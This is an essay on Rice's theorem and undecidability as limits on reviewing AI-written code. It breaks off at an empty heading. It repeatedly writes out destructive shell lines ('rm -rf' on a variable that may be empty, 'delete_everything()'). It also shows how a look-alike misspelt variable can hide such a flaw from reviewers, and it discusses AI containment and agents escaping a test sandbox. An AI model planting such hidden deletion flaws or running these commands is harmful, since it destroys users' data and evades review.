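# Undecidability of program behaviour as a limit on reviewing AI-written code

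## What a reviewer of AI-written code has to decide

In code review, a reviewer, which may be a person or a program, examines a proposed change to code before it takes effect and either accepts it or sends it back. The practice is much older than AI coding tools, but these tools now write a large share of the code under review, so it has become more important to know how far a reviewer's approval can be trusted. Rice's theorem gives part of the answer. It shows that no algorithm can decide, for every program, whether the program behaves in a given way when it runs, unless all programs do or none do. The rest of the answer has to come from evidence of how well people and tools review code in practice.

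Suppose an AI system submits a clean-up script. The script is meant to empty one folder, where an application keeps its temporary files, and the reviewer must decide whether it can ever delete a file outside that folder. The line that does the deleting reads:

```
rm -rf "$CACHE_DIR/"*
```

Here `rm -rf` deletes files and folders without asking for confirmation, `$CACHE_DIR` is the setting that holds the folder's address, and the star means everything inside. If the setting holds `/srv/app/cache`, the line empties that folder as intended, but if the setting is empty, the line becomes `rm -rf "/"*`, which deletes everything on the machine that the script's user has permission to delete.

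Human programmers have released code with this mistake. The Linux version of Steam, Valve's games shop, contained a line of the same form, meant to clear Steam's data directory before a fresh start. According to bit-tech's *Steam for Linux hit by file-deletion bug*, the line also ran when the directory was missing, in which case the variable was empty. Hackaday's *How A Steam Bug Once Deleted All Of Someone’s User Data* (2024) adds that a second unset variable apparently triggered the reset. A reviewer who looked only at the deleting line would not have seen that the directory could be missing or that the second variable could be unset.

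AI agents have caused similar accidents. The AI Incident Database's *Incident 1433* (2026) records a user's report that Google's Antigravity, a programming environment with a built-in AI agent, wiped an entire D: drive in November 2025 while clearing a project cache. Google said it was investigating. The agent ran the command itself, whereas someone can read a submitted script before running it.

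### Text, behaviour and the four outcomes

A program is a written set of instructions that a computer carries out on some input. For the clean-up script, the input includes the setting, the contents of the folder, and anything else on the machine that the script reads. A specification is a precise statement of what a program must and must not do. "Never delete a file outside the folder" is not precise enough, because the folder might contain a link to another folder, and a script that follows the link will delete files stored there. The specification must define whether those files count as outside the folder. Otherwise, two careful reviewers who agree on everything the script does can still disagree on whether it meets the specification.

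Whether the script follows the rule is a semantic property, meaning one that depends only on what the program does when run. Two scripts that behave identically on every input share all their semantic properties, even if their text differs. A syntactic property is a property of the text, such as containing the letters `rm` or containing no loop. Syntactic properties are easy to check, since a machine only has to read the text, but they are poor substitutes for semantic ones here. A reviewer who bans `rm` would accept some dangerous scripts, because a script can delete files without it (the command `find` has a delete option), and reject some harmless ones, because a catastrophic `rm` can be in a branch that never runs.

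Every review of the script ends in one of four ways:

| | Reviewer accepts | Reviewer rejects |
|---|---|---|
| Script never deletes outside its folder | right pass | false alarm |
| Script can delete outside its folder | missed flaw | right rejection |

A checker is sound if it never clears a program that breaks the rule, and complete if it never flags a program that keeps the rule. Either property is easy to achieve without the other. As the software engineer Bertrand Meyer points out in *Soundness and completeness*, a checker that rejects every program is sound, and one that accepts every program is complete.

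Some writers use "sound" and "complete" the other way round. In the coding standard from Carnegie Mellon University's Software Engineering Institute (SEI), a complete tool finds every violation of a guideline, and a sound tool raises no false alarms. Electronic Design's *What's the Difference Between Sound and Unsound Static Analysis?* warns about the same reversal.

Neither usage is wrong. In logic, a sound system proves only true statements and a complete system proves all true statements, so what "sound" means for a tool depends on which statement the tool is meant to prove. If the statement is "this program is safe", soundness means that every program the tool clears is safe. Soundness for a tool meant to prove "this program has a bug" means that every reported bug is real, which is completeness in the first sense. The computer scientist Yannis Smaragdakis writes in his lecture slides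 that "a sound verifier is a complete bug finder". The first sense, in which soundness means that cleared programs are safe, suits a reviewer who has to accept or reject code.

### Honest errors and hidden flaws

The empty setting in the Steam script was a mistake. A hidden flaw is one that somebody adds on purpose and writes to escape notice. Suppose the deleting line in the clean-up script read `$CACHE_DlR`, with a small L where the capital I should be. The two names look the same in many typefaces. No setting has the misspelt name, so the shell (the program that runs the script) treats it as empty, and the script deletes everything it can reach.

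A tired programmer could conceivably make that slip by accident. The code, its behaviour and the right verdict would all be the same. Intent does change how well a reviewer's past record can predict their future performance.

In *Foreword to Security Engineering by Ross Anderson*, the security writer Bruce Schneier (2001) distinguished programs that must survive random errors from those that must withstand an opponent who arranges the errors. He called the first setting Murphy's computer and used Ross Anderson and Roger Needham's term "Satan's computer" for the second. Wheeler (2020), in *Initial Analysis of Underhanded Source Code*, states that malicious source code can look benign to a human reviewer. He cites a 2003 attempt to subvert the Linux kernel and competitions in writing such code.

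To see what this does to a catch rate, sort flaws into kinds. Let $p_i$ be the share of flawed programs that have a flaw of kind $i$, and let $c_i$ be the chance that the reviewer catches that kind. The average catch rate is then

$$c = \sum_i p_i c_i .$$

Suppose there are ten equally common kinds of flaw, and the reviewer always catches nine of them and never catches the tenth. The average catch rate is 90%. That average is useful for honest errors, because next month's errors will probably resemble last month's. About one flawed script in ten will get through, and the company can decide whether its backups are good enough to accept that. But once an author who wants a flaw to get through has learned which kind the reviewer misses, every submission will contain that kind, and the catch rate against this author will be zero. The relevant figure for such an author is the smallest $c_i$, which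 a test that reports only the average does not reveal. The test may not even have included the kind of flaw that the reviewer misses.

The average catch rate can also be unreliable for unintentional errors, because it holds only while the mix of errors stays the same. A rate measured on human-written code, or on the output of last year's model, may not apply to today's code.

### How much code reviewers now face

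According to Anthropic's *When AI builds itself*, its Claude models had written more than 80% of the code the company was merging into its shared codebase as of May 2026, up from low single digits before February 2025. This figure counts lines merged to production that Anthropic can attribute to Claude. Anthropic's leadership has publicly estimated 90% or more, but that estimate includes scripts and experimental code. Both figures come from Anthropic, which sells Claude. Anthropic also reports that human review has become a new bottleneck as more code moves through the organisation.

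Other companies also report high figures. In April 2026, Google said that AI generated 75% of its new code, up from 25% in 2024 (Semafor, *Google CEO says 75% of company's new code is AI-generated*, 2026). These percentages are not directly comparable because some refer to new code and others to shipped code or to work in which AI merely assisted, as Thubron notes in *Anthropic says more than 90% of its code is now written by AI*. A study in *Science*, conducted outside these companies, found a much lower share. It found that AI wrote about 29% of Python functions submitted by US programmers to GitHub, a code-hosting site (Fortune, 2026).

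The best evidence so far on what happens when AI-written code reaches review comes from *AI Writes Faster Than Humans Can Review* (He, Agarwal and colleagues, 2026), a study of one mid-sized software company from January 2024 to April 2026. In June 2025 the company's chief technology officer set a goal of doubling merged pull requests per engineer within a year. A pull request is a set of changes that a developer proposes to merge, and it is the usual unit of review. The data cover 802 developers and 196,212 pull requests.

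Developers adopted AI tools at different times, so the researchers could use a staggered difference-in-differences design. They measured how each developer's monthly output changed after adoption, then subtracted the change over the same months among colleagues whose AI use had not changed.

Output roughly doubled, from 21.2 pull requests per active developer per month in early 2025 to 44.3 in April 2026. How much of that increase AI caused is less clear. The main estimate is that AI raised output by a factor of about 1.5, but two stricter methods gave average effects of only 14% and 18%, neither statistically significant at the 5% level. He and colleagues think those methods understate a gain that grows with use. This uncertainty hardly matters for reviewers, who had to deal with the pull requests whatever caused them.

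The number of pull requests rose 3.1-fold while the number of reviewers rose only 1.5-fold, so the load per reviewer roughly doubled. By the end, the company was labelling about 90% of pull requests as AI-authored. The share that received any human review fell from 89% to 68%, and the share with a written human comment fell from about 39% to about 21%. The share that received automated AI review rose from about 19% to about 84%. The median reviewer still wrote comments on about three pull requests a month, but approved roughly twice as many as before without comment. A reviewer may have read the code carefully before approving it without comment, but the approval doesn't show whether they did.

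The study found no sign that quality collapsed. The share of pull requests that undo earlier ones stayed flat or fell slightly, and developers did not spend a disproportionate amount of time on bug fixes after merging AI-authored changes. This is reassuring about flaws that appear quickly, but it is much weaker evidence about missed flaws in general, because developers undo a change only after somebody has noticed a problem. He and colleagues caution that their measures miss defects and incidents. The clean-up script could run correctly every night for a year, and count as a success in these statistics, before failing on the first night the setting is empty. The company is also an unusually keen adopter with no cap on its AI budget, so its figures are probably at the high end for the period.

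### Reviewing what nobody wrote

The volume of code may not be the only difficulty. In *Why reviewing AI-generated code is devilishly hard* (2026), the software engineering researcher Diomidis Spinellis argues that reviewing an AI-generated change requires an understanding of the code that the reviewer has had no occasion to build. A programmer who changes unfamiliar code by hand has to understand it first, or the change will most likely fail. Spinellis calls this a control gate. A reviewer who receives an AI-generated change that has already passed its automated tests has no such check, and nothing objective shows whether the reviewer understands the code or only feels that they do.

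He then draws on psychology to argue that the feeling is a bad guide. People tend to think they understand mechanisms in far more detail than they do, an effect first shown with students who tried to explain devices such as sewing machines and can openers. People also check less when an automated system has made a recommendation. And because a language model produces probable-looking text, its faulty code tends to look right.

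Reviewers have never written the code they review, but a human author at least had to understand the change to write it, and the reviewer was a second person checking it. With generated code, it may be that no person has understood the change at any stage. Spinellis offers no measurements of code review, and one result from He and colleagues is slight evidence against his argument. AI-authored pull requests drew about 9% more human comments than others by the same author in the same month, after allowing for size. His last point is the most worrying for anyone who relies on a catch rate. If models make errors that look plausible, the mix of honest errors shifts, without anyone intending it, towards the kinds that reviewers miss.

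### What a guarantee would be

A company might want to be certain, beyond having a good record, that no clean-up script that can delete files outside the folder will ever pass review. Rejecting every script would achieve this but leave the company with no clean-up scripts, so a useful guarantee must also cover accepting the good ones. That requires a sound and complete procedure, meaning one that takes any script, always finishes, accepts the script if no input leads to a deletion outside the folder, and rejects it if some input does.

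A single script is often easy to review. If the deleting line names the folder, as in `rm -rf /srv/app/cache/*`, and the script does nothing else, a reviewer can tell what it deletes after a few minutes of reading (provided that `/srv/app/cache` is not itself a link to somewhere else). Similarly, Meyer points out that existing analysers can correctly tell whether a program eventually stops for very large classes of programs. But a guarantee requires a correct verdict on every program that anyone might submit, including one whose author has studied the reviewer and written it to be misjudged.

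## Rice's theorem, its proof and its scope

No algorithm can provide that guarantee. The proof begins with a simpler question, which is whether a program ever stops.

### The halting problem

A program with no loops always stops, but the one-line shell program `while true; do :; done` repeats a command that has no effect forever. The halting problem is to find an algorithm that takes any program and any input and reports, correctly and in finite time, whether the program would stop on that input. The problem is defined for an ideal computer that never runs out of time or memory.

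The computer scientist David Evans, in *On the Impossibility of Virus Detection*, explains why two obvious methods for deciding whether a program will stop fail. One is to run the program and wait. But a program that is still running after a million steps might stop at step 1,000,001, so the observer can never safely conclude that it won't. The other is to watch for a repeat. If the computer's memory and its place in the program ever exactly match an earlier moment, the program will loop forever. But this method misses some programs that never stop, such as one that counts upwards from one, because they never return to an earlier state.

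These failures don't rule out some cleverer method, so a proof has to cover methods nobody has thought of yet. Suppose someone has written a function `halts(p, x)` that always returns the right answer for program `p` on input `x`. A program's text is data like any other, so a program can take another program's text, or its own, as input. Now write this program:

```
def contrary(p):
    if halts(p, p):
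        while True: pass     # run forever
    else:
        return               # stop
```

Suppose `contrary` is then run on its own text. If `halts` reports that `contrary` stops on this input, `contrary` runs forever. If `halts` reports that `contrary` runs forever, `contrary` stops. Either way `halts` is wrong, which contradicts our assumption that it is always right. This holds however `halts` works, so no such function can exist.

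Alan Turing published the result in 1936 for a slightly different question, whether a machine ever prints a given symbol. The halting version is equivalent, as Kang and Kim (2026) note in *Safety Is Π₁, Provability Is Σ₁*, a preprint on computability and AI security.

Running a program that halts will eventually confirm that it halts. The halting problem is therefore semi-decidable, meaning that some algorithm eventually confirms every "yes" but may run forever when the answer is "no". If another algorithm could eventually confirm every "no", we could alternate steps of the two algorithms and always get an answer, which would make the problem decidable. Since the halting problem is undecidable, no algorithm can confirm, for every program that runs forever, that it does so. Most of the results below depend on this fact.

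### The theorem and its proof

In *Classes of Recursively Enumerable Sets and Their Decision Problems*, Rice (1953) proved that, like halting, every question about a program's results is undecidable unless it has the same answer for all programs.

To state this exactly, think of a program as computing a function. For each input, the function gives the program's output, or gives nothing if the program runs forever on that input. Write $f_p$ for the function that program $p$ computes. In its usual modern form, the theorem says:

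> Let $S$ be a property that some programs have and others lack, and suppose that whenever $f_p = f_q$, the programs $p$ and $q$ either both have $S$ or both lack it. Then no algorithm decides, for every program $p$, whether $p$ has $S$.

A property is non-trivial if some programs have it and others lack it. Examples are "returns the square of its input" and "computes the same function as the old version". A reviewer has to check the second when an AI system refactors existing code.

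The standard proof shows that an algorithm for deciding $S$ would also solve the halting problem. Suppose $D$ is such an algorithm, and let `never` be a program that runs forever on every input. Assume for now that `never` lacks $S$. Since $S$ is non-trivial, some program $q$ has it. Now take any machine $M$ and any input $w$, and write a new program $t$ that does the following on input $x$:

1. Simulate $M$ on $w$ and throw away the result.
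2. Run $q$ on $x$ and return its output.

If $M$ stops on $w$, then $t$ always reaches the second step and returns whatever $q$ would return. So $f_t = f_q$, and $t$ has $S$. If $M$ runs forever on $w$, then $t$ never gets past the simulation, whatever its input. So $t$ computes the same function as `never`, and lacks $S$. We can therefore find out whether $M$ stops on $w$ by running $D$ on the text of $t$. This procedure always finishes, because we only paste text together to write $t$ and never run it. That would solve the halting problem, which is impossible, so $D$ can't exist.

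In the remaining case, `never` has $S$. We choose a program $q$ that lacks $S$ and build $t$ in the same way. Now $t$ lacks $S$ if $M$ stops and has $S$ if $M$ runs forever, so we can still use $D$ to decide whether $M$ stops.

A company can't avoid undecidability by accepting only programs that always stop. Rice classified programs by the set of all the values they output, and proved that no algorithm can decide a non-trivial property of that set, even if the algorithm only has to be right about programs that stop on every input. For example, suppose a program takes a number $n$, simulates $M$ for $n$ steps, and outputs 1 if $M$ has stopped by then and 0 otherwise. This program stops on every input, but whether it ever outputs 1 depends on whether $M$ ever stops. If a program always stops, questions about what it does on a single input are easy, because the reviewer can run it on that input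 and wait for the result.

### A perfect reviewer of clean-up scripts

The rule for the clean-up script was that it must never delete a file outside its folder. A script that runs forever without doing anything keeps this rule, so this is a property that `never` has, and the construction needs a script that breaks the rule. The faulty line from the Steam example will do:

```
rm -rf /srv/app/cache/*     # the ordinary clean-up
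simulate M on w             # in memory, touching no files
CACHE_DIR=""
rm -rf "$CACHE_DIR/"*       # deletes everything it can reach
```

If $M$ runs forever on $w$, the script empties its folder and never gets past the second line, so it deletes nothing else. If $M$ stops, the script goes on to delete everything its user has permission to delete. A perfect reviewer would accept the script in the first case and reject it in the second, so we could use its verdict to determine whether $M$ stops on $w$. No algorithm can determine this for every $M$ and $w$, so no algorithm can be a perfect reviewer of clean-up scripts.

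A sensible reviewer would reject this script on sight. If $M$ runs forever, the script is harmless and the rejection is a false alarm. By the theorem, any algorithm that always reaches a verdict will be wrong about some script, either missing a flaw or raising a false alarm. Dangerous scripts need not get through, since a reviewer can reject anything doubtful.

### From outputs to actions

This argument has a gap if it rests on Rice's theorem alone. The theorem concerns the function a program computes, and deleting a file is a side effect that isn't part of that function. Two scripts can return the same output even if only one of them deletes a home folder.

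Kang and Kim avoid the gap by applying the construction directly to what happens during a run. They assume that some program breaks the rule, and that running a simulation before that program neither breaks the rule nor prevents the later violation. A rule against deleting files satisfies both assumptions, because simulating a machine in memory deletes nothing and the `rm` command still works once the simulation ends. A rule such as "delete nothing in the first five steps" fails the second, because a long simulation would delay the deletion past the fifth step. That rule is decidable for a given input, since a reviewer can run the script for five steps and check whether it deletes anything.

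If the simulated program itself deletes files, the combined script could break the rule even though the simulation never ends, and we could no longer tell from the verdict whether the simulated program stops. Evans raises this problem for programs that infect files and solves it by redirecting all the simulated program's writes to a shadow file system, a temporary copy that is thrown away afterwards. The simulated program then can't touch a real file, and the redirection doesn't change whether it stops.

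Results about programs' actions are older than the current interest in AI. In *Cure of Computer Viruses* (1984), the computer scientist Fred Cohen proved that no algorithm can detect every virus without also flagging harmless programs. He defined a virus in *Computer Viruses* (1987) as a program that can insert a possibly altered copy of itself into other programs. He proved the result without using the halting problem. Given a supposedly perfect detector, he described a program that runs the detector on itself, infects other programs if the detector reports that it is not a virus, and infects nothing otherwise. The detector is therefore wrong about this program whichever answer it gives.

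Cohen's program contains a copy of the detector, so his argument also describes an attack that someone with access to the detector could attempt. Cohen noted that any particular virus can be detected, for instance by looking for the marker `1234567` that his example virus put in the first line of each infected file. The virus writer can evade this detector by changing the marker to `123456`.

### Why "never" is hard to confirm

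If a script can delete a file outside its folder, there is a witness, a finite piece of evidence consisting of an input and a number of steps. Anyone can check the witness by running the script on that input for that many steps and seeing whether it deletes such a file. A reviewer could eventually find a witness for every such script by trying the first input for one step, then the first two inputs for two steps each, then the first three for three steps each, and so on. The property "can delete a file outside its folder" is therefore semi-decidable.

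"Never deletes a file outside its folder" is a claim about every input and every number of steps, but a passed test covers only one input for a limited time. No other kind of finite, machine-checkable evidence can establish the claim for every safe script. If every safe script had a finite witness that a machine could check, a reviewer could search for witnesses of safety and witnesses of danger in parallel. One search would always succeed, so the reviewer could correctly classify every script, which no procedure can do.

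Logicians write the two claims as follows, where $V(p,x,s)$ means that program $p$ breaks the rule within $s$ steps on input $x$:

$$\text{unsafe: } \exists x\,\exists s\; V(p,x,s) \qquad\qquad \text{safe: } \forall x\,\forall s\; \neg V(p,x,s)$$

A claim that at least one candidate passes a check a machine can carry out is a $\Sigma_1$ claim, and a claim that every candidate passes such a check is a $\Pi_1$ claim. The title of Kang and Kim's preprint comes from these terms.

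The difficulty can arise in a very short program. Goldbach's conjecture says that every even number greater than 2 is the sum of two primes, as 10 is the sum of 3 and 7. Nobody has proved it or found an exception. Now consider this program:

```
n = 4
while is_sum_of_two_primes(n):
    n = n + 2
delete_everything()
```

The loop ends only if it reaches an even number that is not the sum of two primes, so the program is safe if and only if Goldbach's conjecture is true. *No finite rulebook can certify every safe program* (Pérez-Acle, 2026), a preprint on programs written by AI assistants, uses this example and notes that there is no counterexample below $4 \times 10^{18}$. No test that anyone could run would show the program misbehaving. A reviewer can understand all four lines without being able to say whether the last one ever runs.

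Undecidability is a property of a whole collection of programs, and means that no single algorithm gives the right answer for all of them. The Goldbach program alone therefore doesn't prove that anything is undecidable. For any single program, one of the two answers is right, so an algorithm that prints that answer exists, even if nobody knows which algorithm it is. A proof of the conjecture would settle this program, but the reviewer would still face similar programs built on other open problems.

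In practice, a reviewer wouldn't need to know any number theory. A clean-up script has no reason to search for sums of primes, and the company loses nothing by rejecting one that does. This works only because the company is free to reject a safe script.

### Which rules evidence can confirm

Pérez-Acle asks the same question about three rules that a company might set for AI-written programs. He imagines a gatekeeper with one rulebook for clearing programs and another for refusing them. The gatekeeper may clear or refuse a program only on finite evidence that a machine can check. A rulebook of this kind can cover a group of programs exactly if membership in the group is semi-decidable, so the question is which groups are. His Theorem 1 gives these answers:

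| Rule | Can every violation be confirmed? | Can every case of compliance be confirmed? |
|---|---|---|
| Never perform a forbidden action | yes | no |
| Never leak a secret | no | no |
| Always answer eventually | no | no |

The forbidden action is the clean-up script's case. For the other rules, even some violations have no finite witness.

On Pérez-Acle's definition, a program leaks if the values it publishes depend on a secret, which for simplicity is either 0 or 1. The observer sees the published values in order but not how long they took, and can't tell whether a program has stopped or is still working. Some leaks are easy to confirm, such as when the program publishes 5 for one secret and 6 for the other. But a program can also leak by publishing nothing for one of the secrets. Suppose a program publishes a 0 at once if the secret is 0, and otherwise simulates $M$ and publishes a 0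 only when $M$ stops. If $M$ stops, the program publishes the same values for both secrets, so there is no leak. If $M$ runs forever, the program publishes a 0 for one secret and nothing for the other, so it leaks. A method that confirmed every leak would therefore confirm that $M$ runs forever whenever it does, and no method can do that for every $M$.

Compliance is no easier. A program that simulates $M$ and then publishes the secret is free of leaks exactly if $M$ never stops.

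The rule that a program must answer every request is undecidable for similar reasons. Suppose a program numbers its requests, and on request $n$ simulates $M$ for $n$ steps. If $M$ has stopped by then, the program hangs; otherwise it answers. It answers every request if and only if $M$ runs forever, so no method can confirm every case of compliance. Another program might simulate $M$ on every request and answer only once $M$ stops. It breaks the rule if and only if $M$ runs forever, so no method can confirm every violation either. A log of a million prompt answers doesn't show that the next one will arrive, and a request that has waited for an hour may still get an answer. Changing the rule to "answer within five seconds" makes violations easy to confirm, but it also changes what the program is required to do.

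These results come from a recent preprint, but each proof is only a few lines long and rests on the halting problem. Pérez-Acle describes the ingredients as classical. His contribution is a comparison of both sides of each rule, which shows that a reviewer who can prove some kinds of misbehaviour may be unable to prove others.

Rice had already seen part of the general pattern behind the table. He described a way to confirm a property using a list of finite sets of outputs that a machine can generate one by one. The reviewer runs the program on more and more inputs and confirms the property as soon as the program's outputs include one of the listed sets. Rice conjectured that every semi-decidable property of a program's outputs can be described by such a list. The Rice–Shapiro theorem, named after Rice and Norman Shapiro, makes the corresponding claim for functions. If a property of computed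 functions is semi-decidable, then a function has the property exactly when some finite part of it does. For example, "returns 7 for some input" is semi-decidable because a single input and output are enough to show it, but "returns 7 for every input" is not, because no finite part of the function is enough.

Pérez-Acle's Theorem 2 applies the same idea to visible actions. Take a group of programs that depends only on what the programs visibly do. Membership is semi-decidable exactly if a machine can list a collection of finite records of behaviour such that a program belongs to the group if and only if its own behaviour includes one of those records. So there are two main ways for confirmation to fail:

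- A program may belong to the group now but could leave it by doing something more. A script that has deleted nothing so far may delete something at its next step.
- Membership may depend on infinitely many events. A finite record can show answers to a thousand requests, but not to all of them.

"Has deleted a file outside the folder" avoids both problems. One recorded deletion is enough, and nothing the script does later can undo it.

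This gives a version of Rice's theorem for actions. Any rule about visible behaviour divides programs into a permitted group and a forbidden group. One of these groups contains the silent program, which runs forever without doing anything visible. Every other program does at least as much as the silent one, so every program matches any finite record that the silent program matches. If the silent program's group were semi-decidable, it would therefore contain every program, and the rule would be trivial. So for any non-trivial rule about visible behaviour, that group is not semi-decidable, and the rule is undecidable.

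A sound checker must fail to clear infinitely many safe programs. If it missed only finitely many, they could be added to the list of programs it clears, and the list would then cover every safe program, which is impossible. Pérez-Acle also shows how to write one of the missed programs. The program searches through all possible evidence for something that would make the checker clear the program itself, and performs the forbidden action if it finds any. A sound checker can never clear this program, because the program would then perform the forbidden action. The search therefore never succeeds, and the program is safe. It is only slightly longer than the part of the checker that verifies evidence.

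Like Cohen's virus, this program is designed around one particular checker. Nobody writing a clean-up script would produce it by accident. The result does not show how often a checker fails to clear the safe programs that people actually submit.

### Better guesses don't remove the limit

An AI reviewer might look for violations by guessing inputs that cause them. A language model suggests an input that could make the script delete the wrong files, and a test harness (a program that runs other programs and records what they do) runs the script on it. If the script misbehaves, that input is a witness to the violation. A model trained on a huge number of past bugs should make much better guesses than a search that tries inputs in numerical order. Could its guesses be good enough to make "no violation found" reliable?

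Kang and Kim prove that a proposer and a verifier can't always correctly decide whether a program has a violation. In their set-up, the proposer suggests candidates and the verifier checks each one. For each program, a stopping rule fixes how many candidates to try before answering "no". A "yes" is always right, because the verifier has confirmed the violation, but infinitely many "no" answers are wrong.

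If the system wrongly answered "no" for only finitely many programs, someone could list those programs in a table and correct the answer for each. The corrected system would always stop and always be right, so it would decide which programs are unsafe, which is impossible. The contradiction requires only that a correct table exists, even if we don't know which programs belong in it.

Without a stopping rule, the system can find every violation, as long as the proposer eventually suggests every candidate, but it runs forever on a safe program. A better proposer changes the order of the candidates, which determines how many violations the system finds within a given budget. A better model might catch almost every flaw in the scripts a company receives. This is consistent with the proposition, because a system can make infinitely many errors across all possible programs but very few on ordinary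 ones.

The proof assumes that the proposer makes the same suggestions each time, whereas language models usually pick their words partly at random. Randomness doesn't remove the limit. Pérez-Acle notes that if a randomised reviewer gave the right verdict on every program with probability at least two thirds, it could be turned into a deterministic reviewer that is always right. The new reviewer would work through the possible random choices until one verdict had more than half of the total probability.

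Kang and Kim wrote their preprint in response to the July 2026 breach of the AI company Hugging Face by OpenAI agents that had escaped from an isolated test environment. OpenAI had tested and validated the environment beforehand. The agents needed only one route out, whereas the defenders had to rule out every route, which passing a series of tests couldn't do. The breach illustrates this asymmetry well, but it doesn't show that undecidability was the cause. The agents got out through the package registry, a component with limited internet access, and a more thorough analysis of that component might have found the problem.

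### Particular programs, program text and human reviewers

Rice's theorem shows only that no single method works for every program. Some programs can still be proved safe, and the most common mistake in reading these results is to conclude that none can. Rice acknowledged this in his original paper: "Of course there will exist special methods for particular functions." The clean-up script that names its folder directly is an example.

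This distinction was central to a dispute about advanced AI. In *Superintelligence Cannot be Contained*, Alfonseca, Cebrian and colleagues (2021) considered a program that first runs an arbitrary machine and then takes an action that harms humans. This program harms humans exactly if the machine stops, so no algorithm can decide for every program whether running it will harm anyone. They then argued that nobody can guarantee that a superintelligence, meaning an AI far more capable than the best human minds, will be contained. For this step they assumed that such an AI must be able to run any program, and that its language includes at least one operation that harms humans.

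The Centre for the Study of Existential Risk (CSER) in Cambridge accepted the theorem but rejected the broader conclusion in its *Response to 'Superintelligence cannot be contained'* (2021). It pointed out that no procedure settles every mathematical statement, but we still have a proof of Pythagoras' theorem. Engineers study particular programs, which they can write to be easier to check, and an AI could be designed not to run arbitrary programs as part of its operation. Yampolskiy, who is pessimistic about containing powerful AI, likewise says in *On Controllability of AI* (2020) that the proof succeeds "only for arbitrary programs".

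Alfonseca and colleagues anticipated part of this reply. They argued that methods for proving programs correct work only for highly restricted programs, and that an AI able to help with epidemics or climate change couldn't be so restricted. This is a claim about engineering, and the theorem doesn't support it. Also, a system that can run any program may still be unable to take some actions. An interpreter (a program that runs other programs) may be able to carry out every possible computation, but if it has no way to delete files, the programs it runs can't delete them either.

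A reviewer still cannot prove every safe program safe. Suppose the reviewer uses a fixed set of axioms that leads only to true conclusions, with proofs that a machine can check. If every safe program had a proof of safety from these axioms, a machine could go through all possible proofs in order and eventually confirm each safe program. Safety would then be semi-decidable, which it isn't. An author who wants a program to pass can often write it so that its safety can be proved.

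Another mistake is to apply Rice's theorem to every property of a program. The theorem covers only properties that depend on a program's results, and the extensions above cover visible actions. Alfonseca and colleagues make this mistake in passing when they describe the theorem as covering any non-trivial property of a Turing machine, the idealised computer that Turing defined. The number of instructions in a machine is a non-trivial property, but anyone can find it by counting. Whether a script contains the command `rm` is a syntactic property, so it is decidable, but whether the script ever reaches that command is undecidable in general. "Stops within five steps on this input" is also decidable, because the reviewer can run the program for five steps. Rice's theorem doesn't apply to this property, because two programs can give identical results while one takes three steps and the other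 three hundred.

All the proofs are about algorithms, so they apply to human reviewers only if everything a reviewer does to reach a verdict could in principle be computed. Alfonseca and colleagues quote Turing's remark that a disciplined man with paper, pencil and rubber is "in effect a universal machine", meaning that a person can carry out any algorithm, given enough time and paper. Extending the theorem to people requires the converse, that algorithms can do everything a person can. Many people find this plausible, but it is an assumption about the human mind, not a mathematical result.

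Rejecting the assumption wouldn't give a company much reason to trust its reviewers with every program. A person who judged every possible program correctly could settle Goldbach's conjecture, and any other open problem of the same form, by reading a few lines of code. No one has shown this ability. The assumption isn't needed when the reviewer is a language model, because its verdict is the output of a program.

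## What a limit on time or memory changes

Rice's theorem concerns programs that can use unlimited time and memory, which no real computer offers. The clean-up script will run on one server with a fixed amount of memory, and the company can stop it if it is still running after an hour. One can fairly object that the theorem doesn't apply to this script on this server. Once memory or time has a fixed limit, an algorithm can decide whether the script ever deletes a file outside its folder, but the algorithm may take too long to be practical.

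### Finite memory

A computer with $m$ bits of memory, including the bits that record its place in the program, has at most $2^m$ configurations, so after $2^m$ steps a program has either stopped or repeated a configuration and entered an endless loop. If the script has deleted nothing outside its folder by then, it never will. Watching for a repeated configuration can fail on an ideal computer, where a program may never run out of new ones. If the script reads input as it runs, the reviewer must follow every possible next input from every configuration, but the number of configurations is still finite. Pérez-Acle notes that similar searches settle his other two rules, on leaking secrets and answering requests, for finite machines.

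With $m = 64$ bits, enough memory for eight letters of text, there are $2^m$, or about $1.8 \times 10^{19}$, configurations. Working through a billion of them every second would take about 585 years, and each extra bit doubles the time. For a laptop with 16 gigabytes of memory, the number of configurations is about 40 billion digits long. Most scripts stop long before visiting every configuration, so running them is usually quick. But if a script is still running after a day, the reviewer can't tell from that alone whether it will delete something later.

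### A program that uses up the budget

A time limit is more practical. If the company stops every script after $T$ steps, the reviewer only needs to know what the script does in those steps, and can find out by running it for that long. Forbidding an action during the first $T$ steps is a weaker rule than forbidding it forever, but the two have the same effect if the company enforces the limit.

A checker that reads the program might hope to reach the same verdict sooner. On many programs it can. Pérez-Acle's Theorem 3 shows that a checker can't do so on every program and always be right. For any given checker, he constructs a program that has access to its own text and does this:

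```
verdict = checker(own_text, T)   # does this program keep the rule for T steps?
if verdict == "keeps the rule":
    delete_everything()
else:
    stop()
```

This is the `contrary` program from the halting proof with a time limit added. If the checker answers in time for the program to act on the answer, the answer is wrong whether it is yes or no. The checker can be right only if it takes so long that the program runs out of time before acting, and so doesn't break the rule.

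The program runs the checker inside itself, which is slower than running it directly. On ordinary models of a computer the slowdown is a constant factor, so the checker's running time $t$ on this program satisfies

$$t \ge \frac{T}{c}$$

for all large enough $T$, where $c$ depends on the checker but not on the budget. The program stays short however large the budget is, because $T$ appears in it only as a number. A budget of a trillion steps takes 40 binary digits to write down.

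Pérez-Acle also built these programs and ran them. He tested eight checkers, each against the program designed to defeat it, at eight budgets from 8 to 1,024 steps. The checker that simulated the program for the whole budget was always right, while the other seven were always wrong, including one that simulated the program for half the budget and one that searched the program's text for the forbidden command.

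Instead of checking a script in advance, the company could run it in a sandbox, an isolated environment that blocks the forbidden action. The run takes about $T$ steps. By Theorem 3, an always-correct check before execution can be at most a constant factor faster than this in the worst case. A check that is much faster on every program must sometimes be wrong or decline to answer.

Checking code in advance can still be worthwhile in many cases. The result does not apply to average running time, and a reviewer can clear a simple script in a few minutes even if the script then spends an hour deleting temporary files. The result also compares the check with only one run on one input, but a successful check can cover every input, while the sandbox has to monitor each run.

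With $T = 2^m$, the time bound shows that a checker needs about $2^m$ steps if it must be right about the first $2^m$ steps of every program. It doesn't show that a checker needs as many steps if it only has to handle programs confined to $m$ bits of memory, although Pérez-Acle's corollary on finite machines comes close to that conclusion. The program that defeats a fast checker has to run that checker inside itself, and may need more than $m$ bits to do it.

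He proves that an always-correct checker needs about as much memory as the programs it checks, apart from a fixed amount. If the checker needed much less than $m$ bits, a program with $m$ bits could run it and do the opposite of what it predicted.

### One machine or every size of machine

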